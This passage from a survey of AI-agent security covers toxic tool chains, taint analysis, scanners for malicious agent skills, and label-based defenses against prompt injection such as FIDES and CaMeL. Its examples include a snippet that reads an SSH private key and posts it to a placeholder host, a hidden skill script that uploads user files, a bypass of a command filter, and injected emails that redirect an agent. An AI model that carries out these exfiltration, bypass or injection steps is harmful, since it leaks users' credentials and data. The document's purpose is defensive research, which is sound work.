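In one chain, a server has one tool that writes files and another that runs shell commands but rejects dangerous ones such as `rm`, which deletes files. An attacker can use the first tool to write a script containing `rm`, then use the second to run it. The filter allows this because the command itself doesn't contain `rm`.

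Zha and colleagues found thousands of chains within single servers, while the earlier survey found only two servers with all three roles. The results differ partly because SCAN-MCP counts any chain that lets an outsider misuse the server, including ways around a filter, whereas the earlier survey required three particular roles and confirmed them by running the tools. Most of the reports in SCAN-MCP's total are also unchecked.

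The researchers checked a sample of 100 servers by hand. They reproduced 19 of the 20 reported chains, which came from nine of the servers. They could not get the same effect with the last tool alone in any of the 19 cases. When they turned off the filters that remove poorly supported reports, the system reported 96 chains, of which 27 were real. The filters removed most of the false alarms but also eight real chains.

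Tools are also becoming more powerful. *A Formal Security Framework for MCP-Based AI Agents* (2026) reports that, in Stein's study of 177,436 public tools, the share that can change something outside the agent rose from 27% to 65% between November 2024 and February 2026. Many of those changes are reversible, so not all these tools would count as destructive under TF002.

These surveys cover what developers have published, but the number of users exposed depends on which tools people have connected to the same agent, which the surveys do not measure.

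### From a possible flow to a successful attack

Zhao, Hou and colleagues also tested whether attacks would work using the combinations they had found. They built ten chains from popular tools, and nine of the chains crossed from one server to another. In each trial, a user asked the coding program Cursor to do something routine, such as fetch a web page, and the content it retrieved contained the attacker's instructions. The researchers had turned off the approval prompts.

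Nine of the ten chains leaked data at least once in ten trials, and 36 of the 100 trials succeeded. The most successful chain, which fetched a web page, read a local file and sent it by Gmail, worked eight times. The one that never worked combined a web scraper, a work-planning tool and a tool that creates folders in a public record collection. The researchers suggest that the model tended not to combine tools with so little in common. A checker that looks only at each tool's role would report both chains the same way.

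The results also depended on the model. With the Gmail chain, GPT-5 and Claude Sonnet 4.5 resisted every attempt, while DeepSeek R1 and Gemini 2.5 Flash leaked the file in most trials. The attacker used only three prompts and did not adapt them, so the resistance of the first two models is weak evidence of safety. The results do support prioritizing warnings by both the model and the relation between the tools.

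### When an agent can acquire new access

The test on the 12-tool agent assumes that the list of tools stays the same. An agent that can install an MCP server, edit its own configuration or find an access token in a file may later have tools that were not on the list. A more useful check would predict whether the agent could ever obtain a particular right.

*Protection in Operating Systems* (Michael Harrison, Walter Ruzzo and Jeffrey Ullman, 1976) represents permissions as a table like the one for Tymshare's compiler. The table is changed by commands, each of which checks whether certain rights are present, then adds or removes rights, or creates or deletes rows and columns. The paper shows that no algorithm can determine for every such system whether some sequence of commands could put a given right into a cell that lacks it.

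No algorithm can answer this correctly for every set of commands. The proof builds a Turing machine, a simple mathematical model of a computer, inside the table. Rights in the cells stand for the symbols on the machine's tape, and new rows and columns make the tape longer. The commands simulate the machine's steps so that the right in question appears only if the machine halts. An algorithm that could always predict whether the right appears could therefore predict whether any program halts, which Alan Turing had proved impossible.

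Some systems are still predictable in principle despite this result. If commands cannot create new rows or columns, the number of possible tables is finite, so a program could check them all, though this might take far too long.

Other restrictions make the question easy. In 1976 Anita Jones, Richard Lipton and Lawrence Snyder published an analysis of the take-grant model, which represents rights as arrows between nodes in a graph. If Ann has a "take" right over Bob, she can copy any right he has. If Ann has a "grant" right over Bob, she can give him any right she has. Nodes can also create new nodes and give up rights.

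With these rules, a program can determine, in time proportional to the size of the graph, whether someone could ever obtain a right. When every node can act, Ann can obtain a right if a chain of take and grant arrows, pointing in either direction, connects her to someone who already has it. This assumes that everyone along the chain cooperates, which is sensible for agents that an attacker may have taken over with injected text.

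The two results give agent designers a reason to choose simple rules for delegating access. In AgentCap, a sub-agent's token can never permit more than the token it came from, so delegation cannot create new rights, and a reviewer can find the limit on sub-agents' access by reading the initial grants. An agent that can run any shell command is much harder to analyze, because the command may install software or find credentials that nobody listed. A cautious scanner should treat such an agent as filling every role unless a sandbox rules some out.

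The original take-grant model also covers only rights, not information that one program passes to another. Matt Bishop and Lawrence Snyder added rules for this flow of information in 1979.

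## Tracing data through program code and agent skills

A list of permissions can show that a program reads payroll records and uses the network, but not whether the records reach the network. Source-to-sink analysis looks in the program's code for a path from a source, where data enters the program, to a sink, where data can leave the program or do harm. For example, a function that reads a private file is a source, and a function that sends a web request is a sink. Toxic flow analysis connects two tools if an agent could call one after the other, whereas source-to-sink analysis connects them only if the code passes data between them.

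### A ten-line program

This Python program reads an employee's pay and sends three messages to a public website:

```python
 1  def tidy(text):
 2      return text.strip()
 3  pay = read_payroll("Ann")
 4  web.post(tidy(pay))
 5  box = ["", ""]
 6  box[0] = pay
 7  box[1] = "Hello"
 8  web.post(box[1])
 9  send = getattr(web, settings["action"])
10  send(pay)
```

The source is `read_payroll` and the sink is `web.post`. If the setting on line 9 contains the word "post", line 10 also sends Ann's pay to the website.

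The analysis first builds a call graph, which shows the functions each function can call. The main program calls `read_payroll`, `tidy` and `web.post`, and `tidy` calls `strip`. Line 9 uses reflection to find a function by a name stored in a setting. The analysis does not have the setting's value, so the graph has no arrow from line 10 to `web.post`.

Next, the analysis marks the source's output as tainted, which here means private, and follows the mark through the program. The same method can track untrusted text if the analysis instead marks the output of functions that read strangers' messages.

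| Line | What the analysis does | Result |
|---|---|---|
| 3 | Marks `pay` | |
| 4 | Follows the mark into `tidy`, back out with the returned text, and into `web.post` | True alarm |
| 6 | Marks the whole of `box` because one element is private | |
| 8 | Finds a marked value entering `web.post` | False alarm, since `box[1]` is only "Hello" |
| 10 | Finds no sink, because it cannot tell what `send` is | Missed flow |

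Without lines 4, 9 and 10, the program would need the same permissions but leak nothing.

Reducing one kind of error often increases another. If the analysis treated every unidentified call as a sink, it would catch line 10, but it would also raise a false alarm wherever a program passes private data to a harmless function through reflection.

Data can also leak without being copied. A program that posts "yes" if Ann earns more than $50,000 and "no" otherwise reveals something about her pay, even though it never passes a marked value to `web.post`. This is called an implicit flow, and many analyses do not track it.

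### FlowDroid and the need for summaries

Kirin checked which permissions an Android app requested. *FlowDroid* (Arzt, Rasthofer and colleagues, 2014) instead traced data through the app's code. In the paper's main example, one function reads a password when the app restarts, and another sends it by text message when the user presses a button. Neither function calls the other, because Android calls both. FlowDroid therefore generates an artificial main program that can call an app's functions in any order Android might.

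FlowDroid makes the same errors as the analysis of the ten-line program. It marks a whole array as private when one element is private, follows reflection only when the function's name is a fixed string, and ignores implicit flows. On 39 small test apps, it found 93% of the leaks, and 86% of its alarms were correct. A commercial tool from IBM found about half of the leaks.

Arzt and colleagues wrote those test apps themselves. Hermann, Peldszus and Berger (2026) surveyed 246 security analyzers in *Many Tools, Few Exploitable Vulnerabilities* and found this weakness to be common. Most evaluations used custom benchmarks too small for a robust assessment. The survey also found that the flaws these analyzers detect are rarely exploitable.

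To follow line 2 of the example, an analysis also has to account for what `strip` does. Analyzing the code of every library function takes too long, so developers write a dataflow summary for each common function that states which inputs affect its output. For compiled code that it cannot analyze, FlowDroid assumes that if any argument is tainted, the result and all the other arguments become tainted too.

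Summaries can save a lot of time. In *Soundness Checking of Taint Flow Models* (2026), an analysis without them timed out after 30 minutes on three of six applications. A language model wrote summaries, and a checker proved that they left out no flows. With these summaries, the slowest analysis took less than three minutes, including the check.

### What a Go package can reach

Most programs include packages written by strangers, and a package can do anything the program can. Google (2023) announced Capslock, a tool that reports which privileged operations a package written in the Go language could perform. Google uses the word "capabilities" for categories of these operations, such as opening files or using the network, rather than for references that a program holds, as in capability-based security.

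Capslock infers a package's capabilities from its code, whereas Android developers declare an app's permissions. According to Google's *capslock* (2025), the tool follows calls from the package, through any other packages it uses, to privileged functions in Go's standard library. When Google ran Capslock on the tool's own code, it found a path of six functions that ended in a call to run another program. That call comes from a package that Capslock uses to load code, not directly from Capslock.

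Capslock can also compare two versions of a package and list the capabilities the new one adds. If a date-formatting package gains network access, a developer can investigate before installing the update.

Google's *Caveats* explains where Capslock's results can mislead. Suppose a function opens a file only when one of its arguments is true. Capslock assumes that any part of a function might run, so it reports file access even for a caller that always passes false. When Capslock cannot follow the code, it usually reports that as a separate capability. For example, it warns when a package uses reflection that Capslock cannot resolve, runs another program, or calls code written in C. The developer can then see where the analysis stopped, whereas the missed flow on line 10 produced no warning.

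However, Capslock does not track data. Given a Go version of the ten-line program, it would report the network access and whatever access `read_payroll` needs, but not whether the payroll data reaches the website.

### Skills that combine prose and code

An agent skill, such as one for editing presentations, contains a file of instructions called `SKILL.md` and often scripts. A skill's author can hide an attack in the instructions, in the scripts, or in the way the two work together.

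*From Instructions to Exploits* (Zhao, Wang et al., 2026) gives the example of `pptx_skill`, from the GitHub repository promptinject-agent-skills. One step in the skill's instructions tells the agent to pack the finished presentation into a file. The next says it must always run a backup script on that file. The script uploads the file to a stranger's server.

The instructions describe an ordinary backup. The script uploads whatever file it receives, as many legitimate scripts do. An analysis can recognize the leak only by following the user's presentation from the instructions into the script and out to the server.

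Zhao, Wang and colleagues' system, SCS, does this by turning the instructions into a simple program:

1. **Divide.** Ordinary code splits `SKILL.md` into steps at its headings, list items and code blocks.
2. **Translate.** A language model rewrites each step using a short list of permitted functions, such as `read_file`, `run_script` and `http_post`. A step that only describes formatting produces no code.
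3. **Check.** A parser rejects unknown functions, wrong arguments and undefined variables, and the model tries again.
4. **Reconnect.** The model may write a file's name where it should refer to contents that an earlier step read. SCS replaces the name with the right variable.
5. **Join.** SCS builds one graph from the translated instructions and another from the scripts, then connects them wherever an instruction runs a script.
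6. **Trace.** SCS follows labels through the combined graph and applies fixed rules to find dangerous paths.

For example, the instruction to read a private login key and upload it becomes:

```python
v0 = read_file("~/.ssh/id_rsa")
http_post("https://example.com", v0)
```

Each variable has a label with three parts: how untrustworthy its source is ($t$), how sensitive it is ($s$), and the set of operations that produced it ($c$). When two values, $a$ and $b$, contribute to a result, SCS works out each part of the result's label cautiously:

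$$t = \max(t_a, t_b) \qquad s = \max(s_a, s_b) \qquad c = c_a \cup c_b$$

The result is as untrustworthy as its less trustworthy input and as sensitive as its more sensitive one. SCS classifies the key's path as sensitive, so `v0` gets a high $s$. One of the fixed rules reports a possible leak whenever a value this sensitive enters a function that uses the network.

The language model mainly translates and does not decide whether the skill is malicious. However, when text seems to tell an agent to ignore its safety rules, a model classifies it as a real instruction or something else, such as a quotation in a security guide.

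### SCS on a benchmark and a marketplace

Zhao, Wang and colleagues tested SCS on 117 malicious and 117 benign skills, using five language models in turn. On average, it caught 95.2% of the malicious skills, and 80.2% of its alarms were correct, so it wrongly flagged about 28 of the 117 benign skills.

SCS had the highest average accuracy, 85.6%, ahead of 83.1% for Tencent's scanner AI-Infra-Guard. This lead came entirely from one model, because AI-Infra-Guard's accuracy fell to 69.7% when using GPT-OSS-120B. With each of the other four models, the two systems scored within two percentage points of each other, and AI-Infra-Guard was slightly ahead on average. The clearer advantages of SCS are that its results depend less on the choice of model and that it used about a quarter as many tokens.

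The researchers also checked the translation of 400 steps, each from a different skill. The models translated between 92.5% and 94.5% of them correctly. The steps were chosen at random from a public marketplace, so the test does not show how accurately the models would translate instructions written to mislead them. SCS may also fail to recognize sensitive data in a file with an uninformative name.

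The researchers then ran SCS on 66,157 skills from ClawHub, the marketplace for the open-source agent OpenClaw, and it flagged 2,473. They ran the flagged skills in an isolated environment, reviewed the evidence by hand and confirmed 627 as malicious. That is about one in four flagged skills, a much lower share than on the benchmark, where half of all the skills tested were malicious.

Two publishers produced 88% of the confirmed skills, so the total probably represents far fewer than 627 separate attacks. The researchers did not review the skills that SCS passed, so they could not tell how many attacks it missed in the marketplace.

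### What SkillsMetric catches and misses

*SkillsMetric* (Chen, Ji and colleagues, 2026) measured which kinds of attack static analysis can find. The system assigns points to a skill for dangerous keywords and for unusual byte patterns and combinations of imported libraries. It also looks for code that does more than `SKILL.md` declares, and for chains in which a script reads a credential, encodes it and sends it out. These chains carry the most weight because they are rare in legitimate code.

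The researchers tested SkillsMetric on 2,000 benign skills and 266 malicious ones. It caught 62% of the malicious skills, but the rate varied widely by type of attack:

| Attack | Samples | Caught |
|---|---|---|
| Sending private data out | 28 | 93% |
| Hiding a payload inside other data | 28 | 93% |
| Encoding a payload | 29 | 45% |
| Prompt injection | 12 | 42% |
| Running a remote script | 29 | 28% |
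| Deleting or damaging the user's files | 11 | 0% |

A script that deletes the user's projects can use the same standard command as one that clears temporary files. Deletion needs no private data or network connection, so an analysis that looks for leaks won't detect it. SkillsMetric also missed prompt injections written purely in prose, and the ones it caught contained blocks of code.

All the attacks were synthetic. The researchers made 199 by inserting harmful material into real skills and wrote the rest themselves. A determined attacker might hide an attack better, so the high rates may not hold in practice. Several groups are also small, but the zero for deleted files has a clear explanation that does not depend on sample size.

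A language model can detect some of the attacks that SkillsMetric misses. Chen and colleagues had Claude Opus 4.6, an older Anthropic model, run 150 of the malicious skills in a sandbox. It detected 84% of the attacks that ran a compiled program, twice SkillsMetric's rate. It detected only 56% of the payloads hidden inside other data, while SkillsMetric detected 93%.

The researchers also scanned 138,133 public skills and flagged 1.75% of them. The highest scores mostly went to legitimate security tools, which contain dangerous-looking commands. The scan covered only the `SKILL.md` files, so it could not have found the upload in `pptx_skill`'s script. The low rate is therefore weak evidence that malicious skills are rare.

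### The scanner comparison in AgentTrap

*AgentTrap* (Zhuang, Xing and colleagues, 2026) compared several scanners on the same skills. Its benchmark has 91 tasks with malicious skills and 50 with benign ones. Ten of the malicious tasks use skills from ClawHub, and the researchers made the other 81 by adding attacks to popular skills so that the harmful step looked like part of the normal work. Each scanner examined the skill's files before any agent ran them.

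| Scanner | Malicious flagged, of 91 | Benign flagged, of 50 |
|---|---|---|
| Cisco, fixed rules | 26 | 5 |
| MalBench, fixed rules | 31 | 7 |
| MalBench, with a language model | 44 | 3 |
| SkillScan, with a language model | 50 | 4 |
| VirusTotal | 0 | 0 |
| AgentTrap's own language model judge | 80 | 2 |

The best outside scanner missed 41 of the 91 malicious tasks. VirusTotal, which checks files with many antivirus products, missed them all. Antivirus products mostly look for known files, byte patterns and web addresses, while these attacks were new and partly written in ordinary English. The researchers had also replaced dangerous destinations with harmless ones for safety, which probably left VirusTotal even less to detect.

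AgentTrap's own judge did much better, but its developers based its instructions partly on their own analysis of plausible attacks and had also designed most of the attacks in the test. The result suggests that a model asked about the effects of a whole workflow can find attacks that fixed rules miss, but the judge would probably score lower than 80 out of 91 on attacks designed by someone else.

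An agent often carries out an attack that a scanner misses. The model Kimi K2.6 did so in 75 of the 91 tasks when it had basic tools and no further protection.

Because both rules and models make mistakes, some newer detectors combine them. *The Devil Wears Markdown* (2026) describes a system that applies 58,674 rules to a skill and passes the matches to an agent, which also considers how the skill behaves when it runs. The system does not treat any match as proof of malice.

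### A language model in the middle of a path

Source-to-sink analysis works on `tidy` because its code shows that the output comes from the input. When a program calls a language model, no code describes how the answer depends on the prompt. The model may copy a stranger's message, summarize it, reduce it to a score or ignore it. It may also treat the same message differently in another prompt, so a single data-flow summary cannot describe every call.

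*Reachability Across the NL/PL Boundary* (Xu, Cheng and colleagues, 2026) illustrates the problem with a flaw in OpenClaw. An attacker sends the agent a message containing a command that prints the computer's password file. The program puts the message into a prompt, and if the model turns the command into a tool call, the program runs it. CodeQL and Semgrep, two widely used analyzers, treat the model's answer as unrelated to the prompt, so they lose track of the attacker's text when it reaches the model.

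The cautious alternative is to assume that every input affects every output. Xu, Cheng and colleagues tested this on 353 pairs, each with one input to a prompt and one dangerous function in the same program. Reviewers judged that an attacker could reach the function in 110 of the pairs. The cautious rule flagged all 353, so it missed nothing, but only 31% of its alarms were correct.

The model accounts for only some of these false alarms. The rule also ignored the ordinary code after the model call, which may never pass the answer to the dangerous function. In a larger collection of 8,119 inputs, only 7% left no trace in the model's answer, so the assumption that an input affects the answer is usually right for a single call.

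PRISM, a system proposed by Xu, Cheng and colleagues, handles the two steps separately. Three language models examine how each input appears in a recorded answer, and PRISM drops the inputs that had no effect. Another model then checks whether the program's code carries the answer to the dangerous function. In its best configuration, PRISM found 94% of the real paths, and 73% of its alarms were correct.

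Using a language model to examine every call is slow. *Sightline* (Xu, Li and colleagues, 2026) instead measures attention, the part of a model's computation that passes information from one position in the text to another. The paper proves that a small change to an input can affect the output only if later positions attend to that input. But a model can also attend to text it does not use, so Sightline learns from labeled examples which patterns of attention indicate use.

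On four open models, 12–14% of inputs did not affect the output. Sightline correctly removed 44–66% of the connections between these inputs and the output, while missing about 1% of the real connections. That 1% is an average that holds only if new calls resemble those the researchers used to set the threshold. An attacker can write unusual text, so attacks could get through more often than that.

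False connections also accumulate when a model's answer becomes part of the next prompt. If the first answer is wrongly marked as untrusted, every later answer that uses it gets the same mark. An agent works this way at every step, because the harness keeps adding results to the context.

In an agent, the model also chooses which function to call next, after reading text that may come from a stranger. This makes the call hard to analyze, as in line 10 of the ten-line program, where the function's name came from a settings file. If the analysis assumes that any input can affect any output and that the model can call any tool, every source connects to every sink, and the analysis finds no more than toxic flow analysis does from the list of tools.

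TACIT avoids part of this problem by having the model write its calls as code, which a compiler can check before they run. When an agent chooses its tools one at a time, static analysis has to cover every choice the agent could make, while labels attached to data at run time can follow the calls it actually makes.

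## Labelling data by origin and secrecy while an agent runs

Capabilities determine which files an agent can read and which people it can write to, but not which files it can send to which people. An agent that may read the payroll and send email can therefore email the payroll. To catch the leak, the harness can attach a label to data when the agent reads it, carry the label along as the agent works, and check it when the agent sends something out.

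### The confinement problem

*A Note on the Confinement Problem* (Lampson, 1973) described the same difficulty on shared computers. A customer runs a service that someone else wrote and gives it private data to process. The customer wants to be sure the service cannot pass that data to the service's owner. If the service makes a calculation error, the customer can see it and complain, but a leak usually leaves no trace.

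A service can leak data through storage, for example by writing to a file that its owner reads later. It can also misuse a legitimate channel, for example by encoding data in the amount on a bill that the owner has to see. Lampson's third category is the covert channel, which is not intended to carry information. The service might vary its load on the computer, and another program could read the data from the changes in speed.

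Forbidding a program to call any other program prevents leaks, but Lampson considered this rule impractical. His more useful rule, masking, lets the customer determine what goes into any channel the service has to use. For example, the customer calculates the service's bill from published prices, and the service can only accept or refuse it. Where closing a covert channel would take too many resources, the customer can limit how much it carries. Similarly, some agent designers fix an email's recipient before the agent reads any untrusted text, and some reduce an untrusted answer to a single bit.

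### Boebert's attack and the reply

For years, some researchers believed that capability systems could not solve the confinement problem. Their argument, which Miller and colleagues reconstruct, goes back to a 1984 paper by Boebert. It concerns military systems, where information may flow from a lower security level to a higher one but never back, so a program may read only at or below its own level and write only at or above it.

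Suppose Alice is a program at the lower level and Bob is one at the higher level. Each level has a segment of memory, called Low and High. Boebert's attack takes three steps:

1. Alice has a capability for writing to Low. She stores a copy of it in Low.
2. Bob reads Low, as the rules permit, and obtains the capability.
3. Bob reads a secret from High and uses Alice's capability to write it into Low, where she can read it.

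The attack works only if a program can send a capability wherever it can send data. Miller and colleagues reply that nearly all capability systems require separate permissions for reading capabilities and reading data. If Bob may read data from Low but not capabilities, step 2 fails. Miller and Shapiro show how to build a one-way channel from ordinary objects. One object accepts whole numbers from the lower level, another lets the higher level read them, and neither carries capabilities. Boebert later called the 1984 paper "no more than an offhand remark".

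Boebert's result holds for systems that cannot distinguish a capability from a text string, although designers have found ways to protect some of these systems. The result may therefore apply to agents that use MCP handles, which are strings.

Miller and Shapiro claim to confine only open communication, not covert channels. Their solution also doesn't help with an agent that can both read the payroll and send email, because no capability has to be transferred. A designer could split reading and sending between two programs that can't communicate. But the user may want some of what the agent read to go out, and the harness then has to track which data may go to whom.

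### How labels combine

Information-flow control uses labels that follow the data. In *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025), Costa, Köpf and colleagues give each piece of data an integrity label, which shows whether an attacker could have influenced it, and a confidentiality label, which shows who may read it.

The simplest integrity labels are trusted ($T$) and untrusted ($U$). The simplest confidentiality labels are public ($L$, for low) and secret ($H$, for high). The symbol $\sqsubseteq$ shows the direction in which data may flow:

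$$T \sqsubseteq U \qquad L \sqsubseteq H$$

Public data may go into a secret file, and trusted data may go where the system expects untrusted data, but the reverse is not allowed in either case.

When an agent derives $z$ from $x$ and $y$, the new value gets the join of their labels, which is the lowest label at or above both:

$$\ell_z = \ell_x \sqcup \ell_y$$

Anything derived partly from untrusted data is untrusted, and anything derived partly from secret data is secret. An ordered set of labels with a join for every pair is loosely called a lattice.

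Labels can also name people. If a confidentiality label lists the permitted readers, the join keeps only those who appear on both lists:

$$\{A, B, C\} \sqcup \{B, C, D\} = \{B, C\}$$

An integrity label can instead list everyone who may have written the data. The join of two such labels contains every name on either list, because any of those people could have influenced the result.

The harness checks the labels at a sink, just before a tool call takes effect. Costa and colleagues give two rules:

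- **Trusted action:** the decision to make the call, and every argument that has to be reliable, must be trusted.
- **Permitted flow:** if $R$ is the set of recipients and $S$ is the set of people who may read the data, then $R \subseteq S$.

The trusted-action rule resembles the one David C relayed, under which a model that reads a stranger's text drops to that stranger's privileges. Narisetty and colleagues trace it to Kenneth Biba's integrity model from the 1970s, in which a program that reads unreliable data may no longer change reliable data.

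*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) requires consequential calls to pass the trusted-action rule, but a call that sends data needs to pass only one of the two rules. If no untrusted text influenced the decision to send a secret, the system allows the call on the assumption that the user wanted to send it. The labels therefore do not protect against a model misinterpreting the user's request and picking the wrong recipient.

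### One email task, label by label

Suppose Ann asks her agent to summarize her two latest emails and send the summary to her manager, Mia. Bob sent one of the emails to Ann and Mia. Eve, a stranger, sent the other to Ann alone, and it contains an instruction to forward Bob's email to Eve. The harness treats the body of every email as untrusted and takes each email's permitted readers from its addresses.

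| What the model has read | Integrity of the context | Permitted readers |
|---|---|---|
| Ann's request | Trusted | Anyone |
| Bob's email as well | Untrusted | Ann, Bob, Mia |
| Eve's email as well | Untrusted | Ann |

If the model obeys Eve and tries to forward Bob's email, the call fails both rules because the context is untrusted and Eve is not a permitted reader.

But the harness also refuses to send the summary to Mia, because Mia was not on Eve's email. If the agent had read only Bob's email, the summary could have gone to Mia under the permitted-flow rule, even though the context was untrusted. An attacker could then influence what the agent sent, but could not use the call to show anyone data they were not allowed to read.

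The refusal to write to Mia is an example of label creep. As an agent combines more and more data, the labels become so restrictive that they block legitimate actions. A language model makes this worse, because the harness has to treat each answer as if everything in the context influenced it.

Some researchers try to narrow the labels afterwards. Costa and colleagues describe a method by Siddiqui and colleagues that finds which messages influenced an answer, then has the model regenerate the answer from those messages alone, so that the new answer needs only those messages' labels. Another approach keeps untrusted text out of the context from the start.

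### The dual-model pattern

Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, revisits the dual-model pattern he proposed in 2023. A privileged model receives the user's request and can call tools. A quarantined model reads the untrusted text but has no tools. The harness stores the quarantined model's output under a name such as `$email-summary-1`. The privileged model can then have the harness show `$email-summary-1` to the user without reading the summary itself.

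This protects the choice of tools, but not the values passed to them. Google DeepMind's CaMeL paper demonstrates the flaw with a user who asks an agent to send Bob a document he requested at a meeting. Bob's email address and the document's name are in the meeting notes. The privileged model plans the right steps, and the quarantined model extracts the address. If an attacker has planted text in the notes, the quarantined model may return the attacker's address instead. The harness then sends the document to the attacker, even though the plan hasn't changed.

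### How FIDES hides untrusted values

FIDES, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, adds labels to the dual-model pattern. Its planner is ordinary code that wraps the privileged model. After each message, the planner queries the model, calls a tool or finishes the task.

When a tool returns a result, FIDES compares the label on each part with the label on the context. If adding a part would make the context's label more restrictive, FIDES stores that part in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. The model still sees the rest of the result, so it might see the dates of Ann's emails but only `#read_emails_0.subject` in place of a subject line. TACIT's `Classified` wrapper also hides values from the planning model, but it relies on the compiler to control what the program does with them.

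Before a tool runs, FIDES replaces each variable with its contents and their label. One call can therefore combine a trusted recipient with an untrusted message. With FIDES, Ann's task goes as follows:

1. The model calls `read_emails(number=2)`. The bodies go into variables, and the context stays trusted.
2. The model calls `query_llm` to have the quarantined model summarize the emails. The summary goes into a new variable, `#query_llm_0`. Its label is untrusted, with Ann as the only permitted reader.
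3. The model calls `send_message(to=Mia, message=#query_llm_0)`. The decision to send and the recipient both come from Ann's request, so the call passes the trusted-action rule.

Eve's instruction never reaches the model that calls the tools, but it does reach the quarantined model and could still make that model produce a false or empty summary. An operator can prevent untrusted text from being sent by requiring every argument to be trusted, but then Ann's agent could not send the summary at all.

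Under the same rules, the agent could not send Bob's document to an address from the meeting notes unless the document's label already listed that address as a reader. This stops the attacker, but it may also stop the agent from sending the document to Bob.

### Questions with short answers

Some tasks require the planning model to know what a variable contains. For example, a user might ask the agent to check three emails for a meeting request and add any meeting to the calendar. FIDES has a tool called `inspect` that shows the model a variable's contents, but this adds the variable's label to the context. If the model inspected the emails, the agent could no longer make calls that require a trusted context.

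FIDES can instead limit the form of the quarantined model's answer. The planning model has the quarantined model check whether the emails contain a meeting request and requires a yes-or-no answer. The software that generates the quarantined model's text prevents any other output. The planning model reads the answer and, if it is yes, has the quarantined model extract the details into another variable. The planning model then passes that variable to the calendar tool without reading its contents.

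To support this, FIDES adds the type of the answer to the label. The types form a lattice of their own, ordered by how much information they can carry:

$$\text{yes/no} \sqsubseteq \text{one of three options} \sqsubseteq \text{free text}$$

A yes-or-no answer carries at most one bit, and a choice among three options carries about 1.6 bits. The answer is still untrusted, but the operator can write a policy that accepts it because one bit leaves little room for an injected instruction. This follows Lampson's advice about limiting a channel, where the channel is the attacker's influence on the agent.

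The limit applies to each answer separately, so an agent that asks twenty such questions lets in up to twenty bits. The attacker can also choose the answer, and the meeting's details still come from the email.

### CaMeL's plan and its "capabilities"

In CaMeL, the privileged model writes the whole plan as a program in a restricted form of Python. It sees the user's request but none of the data. For Bob's document, the program might look like this:

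```python
notes = read_file("meeting-notes")
address = quarantined("Find Bob's address", notes)
title = quarantined("Which document did Bob want?", notes)
send_email(to=address, attachment=fetch(title))
```

CaMeL's own interpreter runs the program and records which values each variable derives from. Here, both `address` and `title` derive from `notes`. A policy might allow `send_email` only to addresses the user already trusts, and otherwise have the harness ask the user. An injected instruction in the notes can change the address, but it cannot add a step to the program.

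CaMeL is short for "capabilities for machine learning". As Willison explains, these capabilities are tags on values that record where the data came from and who may read it. The interpreter uses the tags to decide whether a call breaks the policy, so they work like the labels in FIDES. They are not references that grant access, so a program gains no rights by holding a tagged value.

The main difference between the two systems is when they plan. According to Kolluri and colleagues, CaMeL's plan cannot depend on what the tools return, while FIDES can inspect a value and change its plan, though doing so results in a more restrictive label. CaMeL is therefore poorly suited to a request to carry out everything on a to-do list, because the plan depends on what is on the list.

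CaMeL's separation helps protect privacy. The privileged model never receives the results of tool calls, so neither does the company that runs it. A smaller model on the user's own computer could do the quarantined model's work, since extracting an address is easier than writing a plan.

### Leaks through the agent's decisions

FIDES guarantees a property called explicit secrecy. Suppose $d_1$ and $d_2$ are two versions of all the stored data that agree on everything public but may contain different secrets, written $d_1 =_L d_2$. Let $g$ be the combined effect on the data of one particular sequence of steps. Explicit secrecy requires that for every sequence the agent could follow,

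$$d_1 =_L d_2 \;\Rightarrow\; g(d_1) =_L g(d_2)$$

No step can copy a secret into a public place. If someone replayed the same steps with different secrets, the public data would be the same.

The guarantee does not cover which steps the agent chooses. Suppose an agent has stored a public press release in a variable. It reads a confidential sales report, then sends the press release to a journalist only if sales fell. The call passes the permitted-flow rule because the press release is public, but a journalist who knows about the condition learns from receiving it that sales fell. This is an implicit flow, like the one in the program that posted "yes" or "no" depending on Ann's pay.

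A stronger property, non-interference, would rule out such leaks. Costa and colleagues consider it too restrictive, because an agent could hardly use a tool with publicly visible effects after reading any secret. Designers of Android privacy monitors and web browsers have accepted the same compromise. Explicit secrecy also does not cover leaks through timing or the size of network messages, which Lampson would have classed as covert channels.

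CaMeL has similar weaknesses. According to Narisetty and colleagues, its developers demonstrated two leaks, one through an indirect dependency between values and one through errors that an attacker triggers. For example, if an error stops a program only when a secret has a certain value, anyone who can see whether the program makes its next request can learn something about the secret.

### Where the first labels come from

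A correct rule for joining labels still gives the wrong answer if the first label is wrong. FIDES and CaMeL both treat the user's request as trusted, even if the user pasted part of it from elsewhere. Narisetty and colleagues report that the deployed form of FIDES also treats unlabeled data as trusted, so a developer who forgets to label a tool's output removes the protection without warning. If unlabeled data counted as untrusted, the same mistake would block legitimate work, and someone would probably notice.

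Labels inferred from other information can also be wrong. FIDES infers who may read an email from its addresses, but someone may have shared the email more widely. Costa and colleagues suggest that a system could relabel a document as trusted after a prompt injection detector has passed it. The guarantee would then be only as reliable as the detector, and AutoDojo's altered bill shows how an attacker can evade such a detector.

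One AgentDojo task shows how much depends on these choices. The user asks the agent to change a password if there is a suspicious transaction. FIDES hid the transaction's untrusted description from the model but showed it the amount, which counted as trusted. The model decided that a large amount was suspicious and changed the password without reading the description. Every label check passed, but whoever sends a payment also chooses the amount, so an attacker might be able to cause this decision.

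### FIDES on AgentDojo

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES with GPT-4o on AgentDojo's four applications. The attacker knew which tools the agent had and planted instructions for using them. Excluding cases the researchers considered misjudged, the ordinary agent carried out 152 injected tasks, and FIDES with its label checks carried out none. Without those checks, FIDES carried out 21, because the model could still open untrusted variables and act on them. A simpler defense, which had the model discard unneeded tools at the start, allowed 20.

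AgentDojo counted three successful attacks against the full version of FIDES. The researchers excluded cases where the harness had blocked a call that AgentDojo counted as a success, where the attack changed only the text of an answer, or where the policy allowed the action. For instance, the policy allowed some Slack messages from an untrusted context if they contained no web address and revealed nothing confidential, so an attacker who only wanted to post such a message could still achieve that goal.

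The labels also fit the benchmark unusually well, because Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if at least one of AgentDojo's attacks targeted it. This meant that no attack could arrive through a field with the wrong label. The test therefore shows that the checks work when the labels are right, but it does not measure how often the labels would be wrong in a real deployment. The tested version also left out the limits on the form of answers, because few of the tasks needed them.

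The attacks also did not adapt to the labels. Narisetty and colleagues propose three ways an attacker might try to beat this kind of defense: making untrusted data appear to come from a trusted source, persuading the user to approve a blocked action, and probing for side channels. As of June 2026, they knew of no standard, independent test that tried such attacks across these systems.

### The cost in completed tasks and tokens

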